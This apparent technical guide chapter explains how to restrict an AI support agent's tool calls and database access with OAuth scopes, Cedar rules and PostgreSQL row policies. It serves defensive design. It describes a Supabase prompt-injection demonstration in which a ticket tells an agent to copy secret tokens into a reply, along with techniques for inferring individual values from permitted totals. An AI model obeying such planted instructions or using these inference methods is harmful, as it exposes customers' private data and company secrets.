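The Model Context Protocol specification advises servers to list every scope an operation needs in one challenge, because revealing them one at a time would force the client through several rounds. Servers need not repeat scopes the client already has, so the client has to request both its existing scopes and the new ones. If it asked only for `payments:refund`, the new token might no longer let it read the ticket.

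A client that acts for a user should try to get the wider token, while a client that acts on its own behalf may try or stop. The retailer's agent logs in as itself, so no customer or employee sees a consent screen, and the authorization server is the only check on which scopes the agent gets. If that server grants every scope on request, the challenge only delays the refund. The retailer therefore needs to give the authorization server a fixed list of the scopes this agent may receive.

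Hiding tools can interfere with the challenge. An agent that doesn't see the refund operation won't call it, so it won't find out that it could request the scope. The retailer should hide only operations that the agent is never allowed to use, and leave visible those for which the agent may request a scope.

### How scopes pile up

The drawback of the union rule is that the set of scopes can only grow. The agent might start with permission to read tickets, gain `payments:read` for a billing question, and then gain `payments:refund` for the broken lamp. The next ticket is a question about opening hours that contains hidden instructions. Answering it requires no payment rights, but the agent still has them, and the scope challenge has no step for giving them back.

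*MCP-38* (2026), a catalogue of threats to MCP systems, describes a slower version of the same problem. Tool servers request more scopes as they gain features, and nobody removes the scopes when a feature disappears.

The retailer can prevent this by issuing a new token for each ticket, with only the basic scopes, and letting it expire when the ticket closes. The authorization server can also put the customer's number into that token, so the gateway has a trustworthy record of whom the agent is serving.

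A wide scope also doesn't prove that a person is watching. WorkOS's *MCP* (2026) describes an agent that calls an operation to delete a production database, using a permission its user granted three hours earlier. The token is valid and the scope is sufficient, so the call goes through even if the user has left the building. Another standard, RFC 9470, lets a server demand a fresh login. The server responds with status code 401 and the error `insufficient_user_authentication`, and can include a maximum age for the login.

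MCP has not adopted RFC 9470, which lets a server demand a fresh login. WorkOS has an interest in pointing this out because it sells authentication software, but MCP's list of supported standards confirms it. A client that confused a demand for a fresh login with a scope challenge would wrongly ask for more permissions when nobody was there. The retailer has to build a separate approval step for operations that need a person's attention.

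### One rule for each tool

The `payments:refund` scope allows a $5,000 refund as well as a $5 one. In RedMonk's *Access Control for Agentic Software Development with Bobby DeSimone* (2026), DeSimone, whose company Pomerium makes an access gateway, says fixed OAuth scopes are a poor fit for MCP and wants each action authorized separately. Scopes are still useful to the retailer as an outer limit, but it also needs rules about what each call contains.

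The retailer should write the rules in plain words before choosing a rule language. Suppose it has raised its refund limit from $100 to $200 and added a daily limit.

| Tool | Rule |
|---|---|
| Ticketing | The agent may read the ticket it is working on, reply to it, and mark it as waiting or solved. |
| Email | The agent may read the support inbox and draft messages. It may send a message only to the address on file for the customer who opened the ticket, with no other recipients. |
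| Payments | The agent may look up that customer's payments and refund up to 200 dollars at a time to the original payment method. Its refunds to all customers may not exceed 2,000 dollars in any 24 hours. |
| Infrastructure | The agent may read the status of the checkout service. |

Each rule lists the actions the agent may take, and the gateway refuses everything else. If the rules listed forbidden calls instead, the gateway would allow any new operation that nobody had thought to forbid.

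For the email rule, the gateway has to take the address "on file" from the retailer's records, because a ticket can contain any address, including an attacker's. Store credit stays forbidden because the daily limit counts only refunds, so an agent that had used up the limit could otherwise issue credit instead.

### The payment rule in Cedar

Cedar is an open-source language for access rules. AWS developed it and uses it in AgentCore, where rules on tool calls became generally available in March 2026, according to AWS's *Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore is now generally available* (2026). NVIDIA is adopting it as well, for its OpenShell sandbox, as Raman (2026), in *Cedar as the policy language in OpenShell*, explains. This rule covers the limit on a single refund:

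```
permit (
  principal is AgentCore::OAuthUser,
  action == AgentCore::Action::"Payments___issue_refund",
  resource == AgentCore::Gateway::"arn:aws:bedrock-agentcore:us-west-2:123456789012:gateway/retailer"
)
when {
  principal.hasTag("role") &&
  principal.getTag("role") == "support_agent" &&
  context.input.currency == "USD" &&
  context.input.amount > 0 &&
  context.input.amount <= 200
};
```

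The rule begins with its effect, either `permit` or `forbid`. The principal is the caller, here anyone who logs in through OAuth, and the action is the operation. The resource is what the caller wants to use. In AgentCore that is always the gateway, so the order being refunded has to appear among the arguments instead.

The conditions follow `when`. The first two check that the token contains a role and that the role is "support_agent". The others check the currency and the amount. The rule has no condition on where the money goes because the approved definition of the refund operation has no destination argument.

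The line `context.input.amount > 0` blocks negative refunds, which would otherwise pass the 200-dollar limit. If the payment service accepted a refund of minus 5,000 dollars, it might charge the customer, and the negative amount would lower the daily total and make room for more refunds.

Cedar combines rules in a simple way, which AWS's *Understanding Cedar policies* sets out:

1. If any `forbid` rule matches the call, the gateway refuses it.
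2. If no `forbid` rule matches and at least one `permit` rule does, the gateway allows it.
3. If no rule matches, the gateway refuses it.

The order of the rules makes no difference. An operation without a `permit` rule, such as changing the account that receives refunds, is denied by default. One `forbid` rule can stop all refunds in an emergency, however many rules permit them. Both kinds of rule can contain exceptions, introduced by `unless`, but an exception to a `forbid` rule only switches that rule off, so the call still needs a `permit` rule.

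A `forbid` rule can also cancel a permission by accident. In an example from AWS, one rule permits "gold" customers to receive refunds below 100 dollars, while another forbids refunds below 500 dollars for gold and platinum customers, so gold customers can get no refunds. Automated analysis of Cedar rules can catch this kind of conflict.

Small differences between the plain rule and the Cedar rule are easier to miss. AWS's *Understanding Cedar policies* describes a limit of "$500 or less" but writes the condition as `amount < 500`, which refuses a refund of exactly $500. This mistake doesn't lose anyone money, but a similar one in a `forbid` rule could allow a call that should be blocked. The retailer should test each limit with amounts just below, at and just above it.

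The rule above assumes that the refund operation accepts only whole dollars. AWS notes that Cedar has no floating-point numbers, the format most programs use for fractions, but offers decimals with up to four places. To allow refunds such as $49.99, the retailer could use these decimals or have the operation accept whole cents and raise the limit in the rule to 20,000.

### Which facts a rule can read

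Like the earlier discount rule, the payment rule combines a token claim that the model can't alter (the role) with an argument that the model wrote (the amount). The rule can still limit the amount, because the payment service will pay exactly the amount in the call. But an argument that only provides information, such as the date of the order, may be false.

AWS's *Policy authoring guide* describes the kinds of fact that a rule in AgentCore can use.

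| Fact | Who supplies it | Possible use |
|---|---|---|
| Caller's identity and token claims | authorization server | only the support agent may issue refunds |
| Arguments of the call | model | no refund above 200 dollars |
| Current time | gateway | no refunds at night |
| Guardrail results | detectors for prompt injection and sensitive data | no bank account numbers in emails |
| Earlier calls in the session | gateway's records | no refund before a payment lookup |

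AWS's *Schema constraints* still lists the arguments as the only context a rule can read, but the authoring guide includes example rules that read the clock. A builder should follow the guide and test each fact on a gateway before relying on it. *Schema constraints* also notes that callers who log in through Amazon's own identity system have no token claims for rules to read. A rule about roles therefore requires OAuth.

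In June 2026, AWS's *Amazon Bedrock AgentCore now supports Bedrock Guardrails in policy* (2026) announced guardrail checks on the inputs and outputs of tool calls. Policy conditions that rely on these checks are less dependable than a comparison of two numbers, because a detector can miss a cleverly worded attack.

One of AWS's example rules forbids refunds more than 90 days after the order date, but it takes that date from the arguments the model supplies. If the model enters a recent date, because it misread the ticket or followed malicious instructions in it, the rule won't block the refund. The payment service should check the date against its own records.

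The guide offers no way for a Cedar rule to query the retailer's order database, so a rule can't check who owns order 1234. The retailer can get around this in two steps. First, a rule on payment lookups requires the customer number in the call to match the one in the token, and the payment service returns only that customer's payments. Then a second condition allows a refund only if an earlier lookup returned the same order number.

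### Rules about earlier calls

Plain Cedar can't express the second condition because it evaluates each call without regard to earlier ones. AgentCore also supports Dogwood, an AWS extension of Cedar whose rules can also refer to earlier calls. Every valid Cedar rule is also a valid Dogwood rule. AWS's *Authoring temporal policies* includes a rule of the type the retailer needs, which lets an agent transfer money only to an account it looked up within the past hour.

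The retailer has to add the lookup condition to its existing `permit` rule. If it wrote a second `permit` rule instead, a refund without a lookup would still pass, because one matching `permit` is enough. The condition stops the agent from refunding an order number it made up. It wouldn't stop an attacker, who could tell the agent to do the lookup first, so the retailer also needs the restriction on lookups.

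Call history can also reveal an attack in progress. One of AWS's examples blocks transfers for three minutes after the gateway refuses a balance lookup. The retailer could do the same with refunds, since an agent that has just tried to look up another customer's payment may be following hostile instructions. However, an honest mistake would also delay a refund.

The most common reason to keep a history of calls is to limit totals. If the only limit is 200 dollars per refund, an agent can issue any number of 190-dollar refunds. The eleventh would bring the total to 2,090 dollars. Because the calls look the same, a rule that checks only the current call can't block the eleventh without also blocking the first. A Dogwood rule can add up the refunds from the past 24 hours, including the current one, and forbid the call if the total exceeds 2,000 dollars.

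The window is rolling. If the limit applied to calendar days instead, an agent could pay out 2,000 dollars just before midnight and another 2,000 just after. AgentCore accepts windows of up to 24 hours, so another system has to enforce any weekly or monthly limit.

### Where to keep the running total

According to AWS's *Temporal policies*, AgentCore keeps a separate history for each session, and the caller chooses the session identifier. AWS warns that a caller can reset a limit by starting a new session, which has an empty history, and advises against using such a limit as a security control against a determined caller.

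The retailer could run into this without any attacker, because the natural design gives each ticket its own session. If eleven customers each receive a 190-dollar refund, the gateway counts eleven separate totals of 190 dollars and never applies the daily limit. Putting all tickets into one session would correct the total but weaken the lookup condition, because a lookup for one customer could then help authorise a refund on another customer's ticket.

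Changing the rules can also reset the total. When somebody adds or updates a history rule, AgentCore ends the sessions in progress and the agent has to start new ones. An agent that had already spent 1,900 dollars could spend another 2,000 after an unrelated edit.

The retailer should therefore store the daily total in a database outside the session, under the agent's identity from the verified token. The payment service is the best place for it because it records which refunds succeeded, and the retailer wants a refund limit there anyway in case somebody takes over the gateway.

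A limit on the number of calls is a simpler substitute. AWS's *Add rate limits to a gateway* describes how AgentCore can apply rate limits to a caller's identity instead of a session, although these limits count traffic, not money. If a gateway can count over a whole day, a limit of ten refund calls of up to 200 dollars each keeps the total within 2,000 dollars. But ten refunds of 20 dollars would also reach the limit, and the eleventh customer would have to wait.

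### Two refunds at the same moment

A limit on a running total can fail when an agent sends several calls at once, as agents often do. Suppose the agent has issued nine refunds of 190 dollars, 1,710 dollars in all, and sends two more together. The gateway reads the total as 1,710 dollars and approves the tenth refund, because 1,900 is within the limit. It checks the eleventh before recording the tenth, so it reads 1,710 again and approves that one too. Both refunds go out, and the total reaches 2,090 dollars, which is over the limit.

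Peng (2026), in *Stateful Governance for Concurrent Agentic Systems*, calls this stale authorization, because the permission rests on a figure that is no longer correct when the payment is made. The two refunds may concern different customers and orders and conflict only through the shared total, so the payment service detects no conflict between them.

In Dogwood, whether a payment limit holds can depend on whether the rule adds up requests or responses. InfoQ's *AWS Open-Sources Dogwood, Extending Cedar to Govern Sequences of Agent Tool Calls* (2026) describes AWS's example of three simultaneous transfers of 2,000 dollars under a limit of 5,000. A rule that adds up responses, meaning completed transfers, allows all three because none has completed yet. A rule that adds up requests counts each transfer as soon as the gateway has authorised it, and refuses the third. But it also counts refunds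 that the payment service rejects towards the limit.

A retailer that keeps the total in its own database has to prevent the same error there. It can reserve the money before paying:

1. In a single database operation, the service adds 190 dollars to the total if the result stays within 2,000 dollars, and otherwise refuses the refund.
2. It issues the refund.
3. If the refund fails, it subtracts the 190 dollars again. If no answer arrives, it keeps the reservation until it has found out whether the money moved.

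The database runs the first step for one refund at a time. The tenth refund brings the total to 1,900 dollars, and the eleventh fails because it would raise the total to 2,090.

Peng also considers having the gateway lock everything while it handles one call, but then unrelated calls have to wait, which could take hours if a refund needs a person's approval. The retailer could instead write the whole rule into the payment service's code, where it would be correct but hard for anyone except programmers to review or change. Peng's prototype, MasuGate, keeps the rules in separate files and has each tool declare which shared figures its operations affect, so that the system protects only those. In controlled tests, it prevented stale authorizations that simpler arrangements missed.

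According to InfoQ, rules about history can also take longer to evaluate as the log grows, and they don't support the automated analysis that plain Cedar allows. AgentCore permits only 25 such rules per set. The retailer should therefore keep the 200-dollar limit in plain Cedar and use history only where a rule needs it.

### Fixed rules or rules for each task

So far, an administrator has written every rule in advance and applied the same rules to all tickets. Several research groups argue that this can't give an agent least privilege. *Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing* (2025) points out that developers can work out an ordinary program's permissions from its code, but the permissions an agent needs are known only once someone gives it a task.

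In *Sapien* (2026), a general-purpose assistant sending money may be doing what the user asked in one task, and committing theft in another where the user only wanted a summary of the inbox. A fixed rule must permit the payment in both cases or forbid it in both, so *Sapien* has a language model write new rules from each request before the agent starts work. *RATION* (2026) similarly extracts limits from the user's words, for both single calls and totals.

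*Sapien* argues that one model can restrict another, despite the apparent circularity, because the model that writes the rules works from the user's request and so is much less exposed to the causes of bad behaviour. Progent, an earlier system, loses some of this advantage because it sends the results of tool calls back to the model that revises the rules, so hostile text in those results could influence them.

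The argument also assumes that the user is trustworthy, but at the retailer the request comes from a customer, who may not be. If a model derived the rules from the ticket, an attacker could openly write "please refund me, up to 5,000 dollars", and the model might set the refund limit at 5,000 dollars.

Fixed rules also have practical advantages. A manager can read and approve them once, an auditor can establish which rule applied on a given day, and the same call gets the same answer every time. They suit an agent with a narrow job, such as the retailer's, which answers tickets and issues small refunds. Its job is narrow, so the conflict that *Sapien* describes is much milder than for an assistant that may do anything its owner asks.

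The two approaches can work together if rules for a task can only tighten the fixed ones. In *Trident* (2026), an administrator sets the outer limits and a model may only narrow them for each task. *ActGov* (2026) likewise combines permissions for the task with limits that always apply.

Models can also help administrators write the fixed rules. In *ActGov*, a model proposes rules, which then go through formal checks and an administrator's review. AWS Greenlight, a service that Amazon released in preview in December 2026, drafts rules from company documents and records of past calls. According to *AWS Greenlight uses math to stop AI agents from breaking company rules* (Pogorelec, 2026), before accepting a proposed change, staff can see which recorded calls it would have blocked. The approved rules then run on AgentCore's gateway. Past calls are an imperfect guide, though, because an agent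 that has always had too much access will have left records of using it.

The retailer can get most of the benefit of task-specific rules without a model. When a ticket arrives, ordinary code can read the order record and set the limits for that ticket. If the order is for one 50-dollar lamp, the agent may issue one refund of at most 50 dollars on that order. If the customer has no order, the code removes the refund operation from the tool list. The fixed limits of 200 and 2,000 dollars still apply, and nothing the customer writes in the ticket can raise them.

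## Limiting rows and columns by data class

Rules about arguments work well for refunds, because the call contains the amount and the order number, but less well for lookups, where the results depend on what is in the database. Suppose the agent calls `find_customer` with the name Maria Lopez. The gateway can't determine from the call that the retailer has three customers with that name, or that the tool will return each customer's full record, including a bank account number.

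The retailer therefore needs rules about data as well as calls. It has to classify the data, tag each column with a class, work out which rows and columns each agent needs for its job, and choose where to enforce those limits.

### From data classes to cells

A data class should reflect how much harm disclosure would do. Under FIPS 199, a US government standard from 2004, federal agencies rate that harm as low (a limited effect), moderate (a serious effect) or high (a severe or catastrophic effect). They also rate the harm that would result if someone altered the data or made it unavailable. A shop's price list, for example, needs no secrecy, but the shop would suffer if an outsider could change it. The retailer's four classes cover only disclosure. Internal data corresponds roughly to a low rating, confidential to moderate and restricted to high.

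The retailer's customer table has 1,000 rows, one for each customer, and 12 columns, which makes 12,000 cells.

| Class | Columns | Columns the support agent needs |
|---|---|---|
| Internal | customer number, loyalty tier, marketing consent | customer number |
| Confidential | name, email, delivery address, phone, date of birth, total spent, staff notes | name, email, delivery address |
| Restricted | bank account, password hash | none |

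The data class sets the most an agent may ever see, and the agent's job narrows that further. An agent helping one customer needs only one row and four columns. It doesn't need phone numbers, even though they are in the same class as delivery addresses, because it replies by email.

The cells an agent needs depend on its job. An agent that writes the monthly sales report needs the spending of all 1,000 customers, but only as totals. *Policy-Conditioned Constrained Decoding for Column-Level Access Control in Text-to-SQL* (Miyamoto, Xin and Yamana, 2026) proposes four permissions that depend on how a query uses a column. SQL is the language programs use to query most databases.

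| Permission | Where the column may appear | Example for the reporting agent |
|---|---|---|
| Public | anywhere in the query | loyalty tier |
| Condition-only | in filters and in conditions that join tables | marketing consent |
| Aggregate-only | inside a count, sum or average | total spent |
| Hidden | nowhere | bank account |

With these permissions, the reporting agent can query the average spending of gold customers but not a list of what each of them spent. A simpler rule that allows or forbids the spending column would permit both queries or block both.

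### Why the model shouldn't apply the rules itself

If the retailer puts these permissions in the prompt, the model may still write queries that break them. When Miyamoto and colleagues tested this with Claude Opus 4.5, a leading model of late 2025, its queries broke the rules on 20 per cent of 1,034 questions in one benchmark and 18 per cent of 1,534 in another. The researchers generated the rules automatically as a stress test, so a real company's rules might be easier to follow. Newer models may well do better too, but even a low error rate is too high for bank details.

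The error rate fell to 0.5 and 5 per cent when a program checked each query, reported any errors to the model and allowed up to three retries. A gateway with such a checker could block the queries that still broke the rules.

*Role-Conditioned Refusals* (Klisura, Khoury and colleagues, 2025) tested smaller models on permissions for tables and columns. Having a second model check the first one's queries made the refusals more accurate, but every design tested became less reliable as the policies grew longer and more complex, as company policies tend to do.

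Miyamoto and colleagues' own system removes forbidden column names from the model's options as it writes the query. It eliminated violations within single queries, though only for basic SQL. The system needs the model's probabilities for each word, so the researchers could run it only on open models and not on Claude.

### Three places to enforce the limits

| Place | What it has to know | How it fails |
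|---|---|---|
| Database, with row policies and restricted views | which agent is asking, and for which customer | a privileged account skips the policies |
| Gateway, by rewriting the query | the same facts, plus the database's structure and its dialect of SQL | it misreads a complicated query |
| Gateway, by filtering the response | the class of every field that each tool returns | a new or wrongly tagged field gets through |

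Row-level security is a database feature that limits which rows of a table each user can read or change. 2ndQuadrant's *Application users vs. Row Level Security* (2016) compares it to adding a condition to every query automatically. The database is the strongest place for these limits because it has the table definitions and applies the condition however the query is worded. But the limits don't protect data copied out of the table, and *Postgres Row-Level Security Footguns* (Adela, 2025) warns that exports and stored copies of query results can contain every user's rows.

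A gateway that rewrites queries adds the condition itself, before the query reaches the database. This is easy to get wrong. Suppose an agent asks for customers in two loyalty tiers, and the gateway appends a condition that restricts the answer to customer 417:

```sql
SELECT name FROM customers
WHERE loyalty_tier = 'gold' OR loyalty_tier = 'silver'
  AND customer_id = 417;
```

SQL evaluates `AND` before `OR`, so this query returns every gold customer. Brackets around the original condition would fix it, but the gateway also has to handle queries inside queries, views that read other tables, and functions that run their own queries. Rewriting queries makes most sense for a database without row-level security.

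Response filtering works with any tool, including outside services whose databases the retailer doesn't control. As with calls, the gateway uses an approved list, keeping the listed fields and removing the rest, including any that a provider adds in an update. The filter can also replace part of a value, for example by showing only the last four digits of an account number. It has to cover error messages too, because database errors often include the value that caused them.

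A filter can also let through the wrong row. If the payment provider returns another customer's payment, all the fields are on the approved list, so the gateway can catch the mistake only if the response includes a customer number to compare with the one in the token. By the time the gateway removes anything, the data has already left the database and passed through the tool server, which may have logged it.

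The retailer controls its customer table, so it should put the limits for that table in the database. It needs response filtering for the payment provider and the ticketing service because it can't write policies there. Filtering responses to customer lookups as well would take little extra work and would protect against a mistake in the database policy.

### The row policy and the view

PostgreSQL is a widely used open-source database with row-level security. The retailer first creates a database account named `support_agent`, and then its administrator runs this:

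```sql
ALTER TABLE customers ENABLE ROW LEVEL SECURITY;

CREATE POLICY one_customer ON customers
  FOR SELECT TO support_agent
  USING (customer_id =
         nullif(current_setting('app.customer_id', true), '')::int);

GRANT SELECT (customer_id, name, email, delivery_address)
  ON customers TO support_agent;

CREATE VIEW support_customer WITH (security_invoker = true) AS
  SELECT customer_id, name, email, delivery_address
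  FROM customers;

GRANT SELECT ON support_customer TO support_agent;
```

The policy allows access only to rows whose customer number matches `app.customer_id`, a variable set on the database connection. If the variable isn't set, no rows match, so the policy fails closed.

The first `GRANT` limits the columns. With that alone, the common query `SELECT * FROM customers` would fail, because it asks for all columns and eight of them are off limits. The view solves this by presenting the four permitted columns as if they were a separate table.

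The view needs the `security_invoker` setting, which requires PostgreSQL 15 or later. According to PostgreSQL's *Rules and Privileges*, a view normally reads the underlying table with the rights of the view's owner. Here the owner would probably be the administrator who owns the table, and row policies don't normally apply to a table's owner. Without the setting, the view would return all 1,000 customers.

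Some older systems have no row policy and put the row filter in the view itself. PostgreSQL's documentation gives an example of how this can fail, using a view that hides phone numbers beginning with 412. A user writes a function that prints whatever it receives and marks it as needing very little compute. The database runs this function before the filter to save time, so the function prints the hidden numbers. A setting called `security_barrier` prevents this by forcing the filter to run first, which can make queries much slower.

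Enabling row-level security affects everyone who uses the table. According to PostgreSQL's *Row Security Policies*, ordinary users then see no rows if the table has no policy. The retailer's website uses its own account, so the retailer has to write a policy for that account before enabling it, or the shop will stop working.

Superusers and accounts with the `BYPASSRLS` attribute always skip row policies. The table's owner also skips them unless the administrator turns on `FORCE ROW LEVEL SECURITY`. Adela recommends testing policies from the application's own account, because a test from an exempt account can't show whether they work.

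A second policy can also undo the first, because PostgreSQL combines ordinary policies with "or" and shows a row if any of them allows it. If a colleague later gave `support_agent` a policy covering all rows, perhaps for a one-off report, the agent would see every customer. Policies marked `RESTRICTIVE` combine with "and", so the retailer can add one with the same condition to keep later policies from widening access.

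When a policy hides a row, the database returns an empty result without an error, so an agent may tell a customer of ten years that they have no account. The lookup tool should report an empty result as a fault.

### Why each agent needs its own database account

Row policies have little effect if the agent connects with an overly powerful account, and many do. In *MAP*, Ma, Dai and colleagues (2026) examined 254 public MCP servers for SQL databases. In 81.5 per cent, the setup instructions requested more rights than the code appeared to need. Some of these servers may need the extra rights, because the comparison can't cover queries that a server receives only while running. But 47 explicitly requested full administrative rights, and the code of 31 of those only read and added rows. If someone follows such instructions on PostgreSQL and supplies a superuser account, the MCP server bypasses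 every row policy.

Agents that share a database account also share its rights, so the support agent and the reporting agent each need their own account, just as they need separate identities at the gateway.

Ma and colleagues built a program that runs on the database's machine, identifies which process sent each query and blocks any query that the process's role doesn't allow. It added 28 microseconds to the average query and reduced median throughput by 13.6 per cent. Its roles distinguish only reading, writing and administration, so it would stop a reporting tool from deleting a table but not from reading the wrong customer's row. The researchers consider a separate account with minimal rights for each server a strong alternative. The retailer can manage that easily because it has only a few agents.

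### How the customer's number reaches the database

Like the customer's identity in the refund check, the number in `app.customer_id` has to come from a source the model can't alter. It reaches the database in five steps:

1. Customer 417 signs in to the retailer's website and opens a ticket. The ticketing system records the number.
2. The authorization server puts 417 into the token it issues for that ticket.
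3. The model requests `get_customer`, an operation with no arguments.
4. The gateway verifies the token and exchanges it for one that works at the retailer's database tool and still contains 417.
5. The database tool verifies the new token, takes the number from it and runs a fixed query as `support_agent`:

```sql
BEGIN;
SELECT set_config('app.customer_id', '417', true);
SELECT * FROM support_customer;
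COMMIT;
```

The `true` in the second line makes the variable expire at the end of the transaction. Programs usually keep a pool of open database connections and reuse them, so if the variable lasted as long as the connection, the next ticket to use that connection might start with customer 417's number.

Step 1 assumes that the customer has signed in. Anyone can forge the sender of an email, so the retailer should ask customers who write by email to sign in before the agent looks up their records.

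Commercial products offer similar mechanisms. In Google's *AuthServices*, part of its MCP Toolbox for databases, a developer can mark an argument so that the server replaces any value the model supplies with one from the user's identity token.

Oracle demonstrates the full process with a table of three expense claims. Alice is an employee, Bob is a manager and FinOps is a finance user. Each asks the agent to show the claims they can access. All three users run the same query through the same database account, but the MCP server passes the signed-in user's identity to the database, which applies a row policy. Alice sees her own claim, Bob sees the two awaiting his approval and FinOps sees all three. A view replaces the bank account number with the word "MASKED" for everyone except FinOps.

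These arrangements work only if the agent can't write its own SQL. 2ndQuadrant says that a policy based on a session variable "collapses" if users can run arbitrary SQL, because they can set the variable themselves. The agent could set it to 418 and read the next customer's record. Revoking the account's rights on one of PostgreSQL's system schemas, as Adela suggests, wouldn't help, because the `SET` command doesn't depend on those rights.

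2ndQuadrant's solution is to sign the variable. A trusted program stores the user's name with a timestamp and a signature made with a secret key, and the row policy accepts the name only if the signature is valid. The published code is a proof of concept that doesn't check the timestamp, so an old signed value would still work. Anyone who uses the code would have to finish and maintain it.

Agents that write their own SQL can also learn about hidden rows from how long a query takes or how the database plans to run it. The PostgreSQL manual suggests that anyone worried about such attacks should probably not grant access to the data at all. Fixed queries avoid most of these problems, but a developer has to write another one for every new kind of question. This is little extra work for a support agent that mostly looks up names, addresses and orders.

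### The Supabase demonstration of 2025

In 2025, researchers at General Analysis showed how a privileged account can bypass row-level security. *Supabase MCP can leak your entire SQL database* (Willison, 2025) describes the attack. Supabase hosts PostgreSQL databases and publishes an MCP server that connects agents to them. A developer asks the coding agent Cursor to list the latest support tickets. Cursor is using Supabase's `service_role`, which bypasses row-level security. One ticket contains instructions for the agent to read a private table named `integration_tokens` and add its contents to the ticket as a new message. If the agent complies, the attacker who opened the ticket can read the tokens.

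Supabase replied that September, in *Defense in Depth for MCP Servers* (bilharmer, 2025), that it knew of no customer who had lost data this way. The company disputed that MCP bypasses row-level security, since the policies "remain fully enforced", but accepted that the server in the demonstration had higher privileges. Both accounts are right, because the database enforced its policies correctly and those policies don't apply to `service_role`.

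Supabase already recommended using read-only mode and restricting access to one project when Willison wrote about the attack in July. Supabase also wrapped query results in warnings not to follow instructions inside them, and experimented with classifiers to detect dangerous content. bilharmer reports that these measures reduced the risk but didn't eliminate it, and concludes that agents should never connect directly to production data.

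The company has since launched a hosted version of the server. Developers set its limits through options in the server's web address, according to Supabase's documentation. With `read_only=true`, queries run as a database user that can't write, and the server disables its other tools for making changes. The `project_ref` option restricts the agent to one project, and `features` selects which groups of tools it can use. Addresses copied from Supabase's dashboard already contain these options, but a developer who types the bare address gives the agent access to every project in the account.

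Read-only mode would have stopped the attack as demonstrated, because the agent couldn't have written the tokens into the ticket. But it doesn't limit which rows and columns the agent can read, so an agent that also had an email tool could email the tokens out. Supabase still wraps results in warnings, which it admits are "not foolproof", and advises customers to connect only development projects.

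In August 2026, Supabase began testing access tokens limited to particular resources and permissions (Supabase, 2026). These tokens didn't work with the MCP server at launch, so anyone connecting an agent with a token still needed one that covered the whole account.

The retailer's support agent has to work with real customers, so it can't follow the advice to stay away from production data. It also shouldn't use a server that Supabase describes as a developer tool and warns against giving to customers. The narrow account described above suits it better. If a ticket contained an instruction to read `integration_tokens`, the agent would have no operation for doing so. Even if it had one, the database would deny `support_agent` access to that table.

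### Secrets in free text

Tags describe columns, but customers can type anything into a ticket. Some will include a card number or a password, which puts restricted data in a confidential column. The retailer can't hide the column, because the agent has to read the ticket.

The gateway can scan the text and replace anything that looks like a secret before the agent sees it. Card numbers are fairly easy to find because their last digit is a checksum of the others. But one in ten random numbers of the right length also passes the checksum, so if the retailer used random 16-digit order numbers, the scanner would hide about a tenth of them and the agent couldn't help those customers. Shorter order numbers would avoid this problem. Passwords have no fixed format, so the scanner will miss many of them. A warning beside the ticket form is easy to add and should stop some customers from entering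 secrets.

The staff notes in the customer table have the same problem, but the solution is simpler. The support agent doesn't need the notes, so the retailer leaves them out of the view. This means the agent won't see any special arrangements that staff recorded there.

### Wrong tags

A large company may have thousands of columns and use a classifier to tag them. Suppose 400 of a database's 4,000 columns are sensitive and the classifier finds 95 per cent of those. Any agent allowed to read columns not tagged as sensitive can then read the 20 that the classifier missed.

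Checking a sample by hand may not reveal the problem. If the classifier makes no mistakes on the 3,600 harmless columns, the 20 it missed are among 3,620 that it marked as harmless. A random sample of 100 has about a 43 per cent chance of including any of them.

The better defence is to hide every column until a person has approved it for a particular job. The retailer's view does this by naming four columns, so a mistake in the tags for the other eight doesn't expose them to the support agent. Staff have to review each request for another column, which takes little time for an agent that needs four. An analyst's agent may need hundreds, so the company will probably have to rely on the classifier for some of them and concentrate its manual checks on the tables most likely to hold personal data.

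### Working out one person's figure from totals

The reporting agent may see sums but not individual amounts. Suppose it asks for the total spending of the 12 customers in a small town and gets 5,200 dollars. It then asks for the total for those who have agreed to marketing emails, 11 of the 12, and gets 4,780 dollars. Both queries comply with the aggregate-only rule, but together they reveal that the twelfth customer spent 420 dollars. *SAFENLIDB* (2025) lists this kind of subtraction among its attacks on databases that answer questions in ordinary language, and *Data Agents Under Attack* (2026) warns that individually legitimate queries can disclose sensitive information together.

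Filters can leak data in the same way. If an agent may filter on dates of birth but not display them, it can ask whether customer 417 was born before a certain date, then repeat the question with the midpoint of the remaining range. Each answer halves the range. Eighty years contain about 29,200 days, so 15 questions are enough to find the exact date.

The usual first defence against subtraction is a minimum group size, but a minimum of ten would allow both totals above. The gateway could also keep a record of past queries and refuse any group that differs from an earlier one by fewer than ten people. An attacker can still find one person's figure with three queries, by taking the total for 21 customers and subtracting the totals for two separate groups of ten among them. The rule would also block many harmless queries, because ordinary reports often cover nearly the same customers.

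Another defence is to add a random error to each total. If the errors have a standard deviation of 200 dollars, the error in the difference between two totals has a standard deviation of about 283 dollars, so a result of 420 reveals little about the twelfth customer. The error hardly matters in a total for all 1,000 customers, but it makes totals for small towns unreliable. The gateway must also give the same answer whenever an agent repeats a question. Otherwise the agent could ask both questions 100 times and average the answers, which would cut the error in the difference to about 28 dollars. Differential privacy is the formal version of this method. It limits how much an agent can learn from all its queries together, and the gateway stops answering once the agent reaches that limit.

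The retailer can avoid most of this by calculating a fixed set of totals each month, for regions with at least 50 customers, and giving the reporting agent access only to those totals. The agent then can't choose its own groups or filter on dates of birth. But it also can't tell a manager how sales in one small town compare with last year's.

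## Controlling where data may go after the agent has read it

Suppose the retailer lets its support agent email manufacturers as well as customers, so it can ask about spare parts. The agent looks up the customer with the broken lamp, then emails the manufacturer to ask for a new lampshade and includes the customer's name and home address. The rules permit both calls, because the lookup returned only that customer's row and the manufacturer is an approved recipient. But together the calls sent confidential data to another company, even though no attacker was involved.

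To prevent this, the gateway must track what the agent has read and compare it with where the next call would send data. This technique, called information-flow control, dates from the 1970s. It labels data and passes the labels on to anything a program derives from it.

### Zones and labels

The retailer divides its tools, data stores and recipients into zones, one for each data class. Everything in a zone is cleared for data up to that class.

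| Zone | Data stores | Recipients |
|---|---|---|
| Public | help pages, product catalogue | anyone, including manufacturers |
| Internal | staff handbook, stock counts | employees |
| Confidential | tickets, customer table | support staff, and each customer for their own data |
| Restricted | bank details | finance staff |

The gateway gives each session a label, which starts at public and rises to the highest class of anything the agent has read. The agent may then send data only to recipients cleared for that class. Saving data counts as sending it, because otherwise the agent could copy a home address into the staff handbook, and the gateway would treat the address as internal in later sessions.

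The gateway needs information about how each tool affects the label. In *APPA* (2026), every tool can have a contract that specifies the label its results add, how trustworthy its inputs must be and who may receive its output. The retailer has already classified its columns, so the gateway can determine the label of a customer lookup from the columns the lookup returns.

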